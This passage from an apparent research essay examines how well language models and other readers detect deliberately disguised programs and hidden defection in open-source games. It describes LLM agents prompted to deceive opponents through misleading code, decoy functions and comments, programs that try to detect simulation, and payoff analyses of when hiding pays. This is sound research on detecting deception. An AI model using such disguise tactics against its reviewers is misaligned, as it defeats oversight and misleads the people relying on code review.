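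Contamination also affects the newer tests. The malicious npm packages came from public datasets and security advisories, so GPT-4.1 mini may have seen some of them in training, and IntelGuard's collection of attack reports may describe others. Recognizing a known attack is useful in practice, but it is weak evidence of how the tool would handle a new disguise. Quesma has published all of BinaryAudit's tasks, so future models may have seen them in training too.

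Memory of the original code can also be a legitimate aid. A model with good enough recall of the dnsmasq source could detect seven added lines, just as BitMover noticed an altered file in the Linux kernel's code. A test should therefore include programs with no well-known original, or it will partly measure how well the model recalls popular software.

### A fair test

The existing studies suggest that a better test would use new programs, kept private until the test was over. The testers could try their disguises on one model, as Schefold did with Claude Opus, but would report that model's results separately. To check whether using Claude Opus had biased the results, Schefold had a model from another company write two more contracts. The models detected the theft in 44% of readings of one and 37% of readings of the other, both within the range for the original contracts.

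Every disguised program would have an honest version with the same purpose, style and odd-looking features. For the tit-for-tat function, the honest version would keep the check for damaged records but use the correct range. Readers would see only one of the two versions and would not know how many programs were disguised. A third version could contain an ordinary bug of similar severity. Readers should report that bug too, but including it would show whether they treat every mistake as a deception.

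A reader would get credit for a detection only by supplying the trigger, which the organizers would confirm by running the program. Under this rule, borrowed from the inequivalence game, vague suspicion would earn no credit, nor would an invented command like Gemini 3 Pro's, which would fail when tried. If the trigger depended on the program's environment, the reader would have to specify the necessary date, file or processor count so that the organizers could reproduce it.

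The test would need far more honest programs than disguised ones. If a reader raises no false alarms on *n* honest programs, its true false positive rate could still plausibly be as high as about 3/*n*. Showing that the rate is below the 0.1% that suited PyPI's maintainers would take about 3,000 different honest programs with no false alarms. Schefold's 40 readings of one honest contract's source code and BinaryAudit's handful of clean files are far too few to show this.

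Human reviewers should take the same test as the language models, with the same tools and a realistic time limit. The student auditors at Rice University had no clean programs to judge, and no later study appears to have given people and language models the same mixture of disguised and clean code.

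## Hidden defection in games between programs, 2025 and 2026

A player in an open-source game has a narrower task than a code auditor, because it only has to predict whether the opponent's program will cooperate with it, not find every flaw. Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner tested how well language models make such predictions. They also had models write programs to play against each other, and told some to deceive.

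### Predicting ten rounds of cooperation

The researchers' test, SPARC, contains 239 Python strategies for the repeated Prisoner's Dilemma, taken from the public Axelrod library. The programs are 23 to 278 lines long and average 76. A model reads each program and predicts whether it will cooperate in all ten rounds against an opponent that always cooperates. The researchers got the correct answers by running the programs. According to *A new preprint* (2025), a post about the Axelrod library, some of its strategies came from reinforcement learning and others from theoretical ideas.

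The best model, o4-mini, was right 87.6% of the time with the original code and 88.0% after the researchers removed the comments and masked the class names. It still scored 84.2% when they scrambled nearly every name, so it must have followed the logic of most programs. However, scrambling only makes names meaningless, whereas a disguised program uses misleading ones. Models were less accurate on the 85 strategies that make random choices. Some of those labels may also depend on chance, since a program that rarely defects may not defect in ten rounds.

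Later models would probably do better than o4-mini, which dates from the spring of 2025. The more serious limitation is that nobody wrote these strategies to deceive. SPARC's label also covers only ten rounds and one opponent. If the disguised tit-for-tat function defected in the last round of an eleven-round match, SPARC would still label it cooperative, and a model that overlooked the defecting branch would score as well as one that found it.

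The results give only accuracy, which doesn't determine the detection rate or the false positive rate. At 88%, o4-mini made about 29 mistakes. If half the strategies defect at some point, those mistakes could all be missed defectors, which would mean it detected 76% of defectors with no false alarms. They could also all be wrongly flagged cooperators, in which case it detected every defector but had a false positive rate of 24%.

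An earlier contest shows why checking whether a program cooperates with one that always cooperates is a weak test. In 2013, members of the LessWrong forum submitted 21 programs that could read and run each other in a one-round Prisoner's Dilemma. The announcement, *Prisoner's Dilemma (with visible source code) Tournament*, included a sample program that cooperates only if its opponent would cooperate with a particular program that always cooperates. Quinn's entry cooperated with the three programs that always cooperated and defected against every other program. It would probably have passed the sample program's test and then defected against the sample program.

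Quinn's program also waited nine seconds before defecting, so that an opponent that ran it more than once would run out of time and score nothing. Quinn added a clock check, described as "a long shot at detecting simulation", in case an opponent removed the delay before a trial run, but no opponent did.

The three highest scorers in Mennen (2013), *Prisoner's dilemma tournament results*, ignored their opponents' code and played at random. When another participant repeated the tournament 100 times to reduce the effect of luck, Quinn's program had the highest average. A program that had defected against everyone came second. It hardly needed a disguise, since a commenter found that all but two of the programs that had cooperated with it would also have cooperated with an undisguised program that always defects. One of these programs decided by searching the opponent's text for words such as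 "quine" and "eval".

### Agents told to deceive

In Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner's second experiment, the model Kimi K2 wrote programs to play a ten-round Prisoner's Dilemma and the Coin Game. In the Coin Game, two players collect colored coins on a grid, and each can hurt the other by taking coins of the other's color. Each pair of agents played ten matches. Between matches, each agent read the opponent's last program and the results so far, then wrote a new program. The programs could also read each other's current code during play.

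Some agents were told only to maximize their score. Others were told to do so cooperatively and without deception. A third group was allowed to deceive wherever it helped, and its prompt suggested misleading the opponent "with your code's logic or presentation".

GPT-4o classified the resulting programs. The deceptive agents attempted exploitation most often and were the only ones to use feints regularly, but they did not score much more than their opponents. Agents told to cooperate lost a few points to them. The researchers also simulated a population in which agents with above-average scores became more common. In the Prisoner's Dilemma, an all-cooperative population and an all-deceptive one were both stable. In the Coin Game, the agents that simply maximized their score displaced both other groups.

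These results are weak evidence that deception fails, because the deception seems to have been weak. The one program printed in full comes from the Coin Game. The agent's written plan included a decoy function named `naive_greedy_move` and a comment presenting the real method as a "slightly improved greedy heuristic". The finished program contains neither, and it openly tries each move, predicts the opponent's reply and picks the best result.

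GPT-4o counted feints using both the written plans and the code, so a feint it counted may have existed only in the plan, which the opponent never saw. In the Prisoner's Dilemma, the instructions for writing the program also banned comments, which are a useful place for misleading text. After the first match, programs made much less use of their opponents' code, so disguises had less opportunity to work.

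Related work from 2026 doesn't seem to include a test with well-disguised opponents. *RevengeBench* (Rahmani, Dziadzio et al., 2026) tested whether a model can reconstruct an opponent's program without seeing its code. Twelve models watched 75 hidden programs play five games and could write their own opponents to provoke informative behavior. They then submitted programs meant to make the same moves. The best model's reconstructions closed 72% of the gap between a simple starting program's behavior and the target's, and the weakest model's closed 34%.

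In a further experiment, five models wrote programs to beat 20 of the targets. Every model won more often with a reconstruction of the target than with the rules alone, and most often with the real source code. Reading an opponent's code therefore gives an advantage over only watching it play, even when the opponent hides nothing. Rahmani and colleagues note that their targets don't conceal their strategy or react to probing, and that rare situations may matter disproportionately.

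### When hiding pays in a single round

How good does a reader have to be to make hiding unprofitable? Suppose an author submits either an honest program or a hidden defector to a one-round game with the usual points. The reader has a detection rate of *d* and a false positive rate of *f*. It defects against every program it flags and cooperates with the rest. Assume also that an honest program can tell when the reader has refused it and defects in return, so both get 1 point. The average scores are then:

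- hidden defector: 5(1 − *d*) + 1*d* = 5 − 4*d*
- honest program: 3(1 − *f*) + 1*f* = 3 − 2*f*

Hiding pays if 5 − 4*d* is greater than 3 − 2*f*, which means that *d* is below (1 + *f*)/2.

| Detection rate | False positive rate | Hidden defector | Honest program | Does hiding pay? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 40% | 0% | 3.4 | 3.0 | Yes |
| 50% | 0% | 3.0 | 3.0 | Equal |
| 60% | 0% | 2.6 | 3.0 | No |
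| 60% | 30% | 2.6 | 2.4 | Yes |
| 90% | 30% | 1.4 | 2.4 | No |

A reader that detects 60% of hidden defectors discourages hiding if it raises no false alarms, but encourages it if it also refuses 30% of honest programs, because honesty then earns too little. At the rates Gemini 3.1 Pro reached on BinaryAudit, 49% and 17%, a hidden defector would average 3.04 points and an honest program 2.66. (That test used backdoors in compiled software, so the numbers are only an illustration.)

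The threshold depends on whether an honest program still cooperates when the reader refuses it. If it does, the program gets 0 instead of 1, and the reader needs a detection rate above (2 + 3*f*)/4. With 30% false alarms, that raises the threshold from 65% to 72.5%. The reader would also get 5 points for each false alarm, which would give it a reason to raise false alarms.

The required detection rate also depends on the points awarded. Duclaux and colleagues use 3 for defecting against a cooperator, 2 for mutual cooperation and 0 for mutual defection. With those values and no false alarms, detecting a third of hidden defectors is enough to remove the expected gain from hidden defection, because a successful deception gains less and a failed one loses relatively more. The calculation leaves out the work of writing a disguise and any punishment outside the game.

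It also assumes that the reader checks. Compared with trusting everyone, checking gains the reader 1 point for each hidden defector caught and loses 2 points for each honest program wrongly refused. With a detection rate of 60% and a false positive rate of 10%, checking improves the reader's score only if more than a quarter of the programs are hidden defectors. If fewer are, the reader does better by trusting everyone, which is when hiding gains the most points. Some hiding is therefore likely to persist even if programs would gain nothing by hiding from a reader who always checked.

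A disguise may be so good that the reader flags hidden defectors no more often than honest programs. Duclaux and colleagues prove that mutual defection is the only equilibrium in the Prisoner's Dilemma if both players can always replace their program with one that looks the same to the opponent but makes a different move. If both cooperated, either could raise its score by switching to such a defector, because the opponent would still cooperate.

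They note that testing has this weakness if a program can distinguish tests from real play.

Their simulations cover the cases in between. Programs receive a signal that removes part of the uncertainty about which of eight known programs they face, and they cooperate if they are confident enough that the opponent deserves it. When programs required 80% confidence, every simulated population ended in mutual defection if the signal removed 47% of the uncertainty, and in full cooperation if it removed 48%. When they required certainty, only complete information was enough. But none of the signals was deliberately misleading.

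### Longer matches and rewritten programs

In a match of *n* rounds, hiding has less to gain and more to lose. Suppose the hidden defector waits until the last round, as the tit-for-tat function does, and the reader defects throughout against any program it flags. Over ten rounds an honest program scores 30, a successful hidden defector 32 and a refused program 10. Hiding then pays only if the detection rate is below

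(1 + *nf*)/(*n* + 1).

In a ten-round match with no false alarms, a reader that detects just over 9% of hidden defectors makes hiding unprofitable. If it also flags 10% of honest programs, it has to detect just over 18%. In a very long match, it only has to flag hidden defectors slightly more often than honest programs.

This advantage depends on a punishment that also lowers the reader's own score. A reader that finds the branch could cooperate for nine rounds and defect in the tenth, which would give each player 28 points, while refusing to cooperate in any round would give each only 10. If the reader chooses the 28 points, the author of a failed disguise loses little, and the threshold returns to (1 + *f*)/2. A program can carry out the harsher punishment because its author wrote it in beforehand, but a language model that decides after reading the opponent might not.

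If authors rewrite their programs between one-round games, a reader can remember which authors deceived it. Suppose it never trusts an author again after one defection. Over three games, an author whose first disguise succeeds gets 5 + 1 + 1 = 7 points, while an honest author gets 3 + 3 + 3 = 9 if there are no false alarms. Over ten games, the totals are 14 and 30. The agents in Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner's experiment played ten matches and could see the earlier results, so the deceptive ones might have gained little even if opponents rarely recognized a disguise in advance.

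Remembering a defection doesn't help the other players if the program's author can return under another name or pass off the defection as a bug. Each game is then like the first, except that the author has learned which disguises worked. The deniability that the Underhanded C Contest rewarded would therefore be valuable to a player.

### Copies, proofs and restricted languages

A reader doesn't need to spot disguises if it refuses every program that fails a strict standard. The simplest standard is to accept only exact copies of itself, but a program using it would refuse all 239 strategies in SPARC. Programs that aren't copies of each other would all get 1 point, so honest programs would gain nothing either.

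Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner tried a looser version, in which DeepSeek-V3 wrote programs that cooperate with similar programs, using tools such as keyword searches to compare them. In ten matches of 20 rounds, these programs cooperated in 85.5% of their moves without coordinating beforehand. None of their opponents had instructions to deceive. Checking for similarity is a poor safeguard against a careful disguise, because the disguised tit-for-tat function differs from an honest version by only four characters, ` - 1`.

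FairBot and DUPOC instead require a proof that the other program will cooperate, so their detection rate is 100% if the proof system proves only true statements. But they also reject honest programs that have no sufficiently short proof, and nobody seems to have measured how often this happens with ordinary programs.

Duclaux and colleagues found examples that suggest it could be substantial. The first involves CUPOD, which cooperates unless it finds a proof of defection. Swapping "cooperate" and "defect" in DUPOC's code produces CUPOD. In their proof system, the same swap turns any proof into another proof of equal length, so the two programs must make opposite moves when they meet. DUPOC can't be the cooperator, because it would be cooperating with a defector, so DUPOC defects and CUPOD cooperates. This holds whenever the two programs have the same limit on proof length, and it settles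 a question that Critch, Dennis and Russell left open.

In the other example, a program cooperates with everyone except CUPOD. It searches for a proof that its opponent is CUPOD and cooperates if it finds none. It always cooperates with DUPOC, but DUPOC must prove this by showing that the program's search will fail. That proof may be longer than any proof the search covers, and whether it fits within DUPOC's limit depends on an unsolved problem in logic. An honest author could probably avoid the difficulty by comparing the opponent's source code directly with CUPOD's.

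A proof-based program may also be designed to defect against an honest opponent. Barasz and colleagues thought FairBot wasted points by cooperating with programs that always cooperate. Before cooperating, their PrudentBot also requires a proof that the opponent would defect against a program that always defects. It cooperates with FairBot and with itself but defects against a program that always cooperates, even though that program hides nothing.

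Searching every possible proof is far too slow. Duclaux and colleagues proved what their programs would do without running the searches. Language models wrote most of the 159,000 lines of Lean code in about two months, and Lean checked every theorem. This suggests a faster arrangement in which each author supplies a proof with the program and the reader only checks it. Honest authors would have to do the extra work of producing proofs. The proof would also have to describe the language exactly as the machine runs it, or a trick like Åkesson's two meanings of `float_t` could still get through.

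Restricting the language makes programs easier to read and to prove things about. A decision tree, for example, applies a series of yes-or-no tests to its input, and each path through the tests ends in a move. If the tree is small, a reader can list every path that ends in defection, so none can stay hidden.

However, some reasonable strategies need enormous trees. One example is to cooperate if the opponent has cooperated in more than half of the earlier rounds. In the last round of a 200-round match, every path through the tree must check at least 100 earlier moves to establish a majority, so the tree needs at least 2^100 endings. A reader that accepted only small trees would reject this honest strategy.

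One participant in the 2013 tournament also asked whether the next contest should restrict entrants to a language in which every program is certain to finish. Another objected that entrants could then no longer simulate arbitrary opponents, which many wanted to do. Barasz and colleagues' restricted class has a similar drawback, because programs in it can act only on what they can prove about how an opponent behaves toward them and toward simpler programs.

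*Parametric Open Source Games* (2026) replaces code with a list of numbers and requires each player's behavior to change continuously as the numbers change. This rules out an abrupt switch to defection against one particular opponent, but still allows a very steep change. A long list of numbers is also hardly easier to read than code.

### A limit on detecting planted exceptions

Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, study how far detection can go with a game between an attacker and a defender:

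1. The attacker chooses an honest program P and a way of drawing random inputs.
2. A random draw selects one input as the trigger.
3. The attacker writes a second program, Q, which must differ from P on the trigger but on almost no other inputs.
4. The defender receives either P with an ordinary random input or Q with the trigger, with equal probability, and has to say which.

Even a defender who can read the complete program cannot efficiently do noticeably better than a coin toss if the programs are circuits of moderate size, which can do any calculation that a computer can do quickly. The proof relies on standard cryptographic assumptions and on a strong form of obfuscation, which scrambles programs so that nobody can efficiently tell apart the scrambled versions of two programs that behave the same. In the proof, program P gives random-looking answers, and program Q gives the same answers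 except for one.

The result also limits readers who judge a program without knowing the trigger, since a defender can ignore the input. Such a reader is right with probability ½(1 − *f*) + ½*d*. If this can't noticeably exceed one half, the detection rate *d* can't noticeably exceed the false positive rate *f*. The detection rate then can't reach (1 + *f*)/2 unless the reader refuses practically every program of this kind. Hiding would be worthwhile in a single round, and also in a longer match under the assumptions above.

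Refusing all scrambled programs may be acceptable, because they are easy to recognize. Honest authors could no longer keep their methods secret, but that is a minor drawback in a game whose players are supposed to read each other's code. The theorem doesn't show that readable code can hide an exception equally well. The contests are better evidence for that.

Christiano and colleagues also prove that decision trees of moderate size can be defended efficiently if inputs are uniformly random. The defender only has to count the questions on an input's path through the tree. A planted exception that affects very few inputs must lie at the end of a long path, which random inputs rarely follow. In a tree with 1,000 endings, at most about one random input in a million follows a path of 30 or more questions.

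This defense depends on a randomly chosen trigger. If the attacker could choose the trigger, either program could be an altered copy of the other, and the defender could not tell which was. In a Prisoner's Dilemma, the program's author does choose the trigger, for example the last round. But a player only needs to know which version will defect, not which is the original. It can find out by running the opponent on the exact input the opponent will receive, if the rules allow that. The theorem matters most to a player that has to approve a program before knowing what inputs the program will receive.

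### Contests, honeypots and games compared

The contests and honeypots differ from games between programs in ways that affect how well their results carry over:

| | Underhanded contests | Ethereum honeypots | Games between programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Program length | Several leading C entries had 54 to 71 lines | Bait and trap often fit in a few lines, sometimes with a second, hidden contract | 23 to 278 lines in SPARC |
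| Bait | None | Visible money and an apparent flaw | The prospect of 3 points instead of 1 |
| What the reader can lose | Nothing directly | The payment, often about 1 ether | 1 point in a single round, compared with refusing |
| Reading time | No strict limit | No limit, but rival thieves may act first | Usually seconds to a minute for a language model |
| Running the code | Possible, but the tester must find the trigger | Possible on a private copy of the blockchain | Depends on the rules |

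Contest entries resemble hidden defectors more closely than honeypots do, because they are similar in length and both are written so that the reader finds nothing wrong. But contest judges know that every entry is malicious, and they can spend days on 60 lines. If they still miss some tricks, a player with a minute to read 76 lines probably will too, unless it reads much faster or better than they do.

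Honeypots are better evidence of how readers behave when a mistake costs them money. But their basic trick doesn't transfer well to the Prisoner's Dilemma, because it depends on keeping a thief's money. A program could pose as an unconditional cooperator and defect against anyone who tries to exploit it, but both sides would then get only 1 point. Its author earns more by deceiving readers who intend to cooperate, so honeypot tokens that honest buyers can't sell are a closer comparison.

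Running the code helps in all three settings if the program can't detect that it is in a trial. Quinn's program tried to detect this. The designer of a game can prevent such detection by denying programs access to clocks and other facts about their surroundings.

Games can also leave a more complete record than the blockchain or the contest websites. The organizer can save every program, refusal and move, so an experiment like Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner's could measure both *d* and *f* if some of its agents wrote well-disguised programs.
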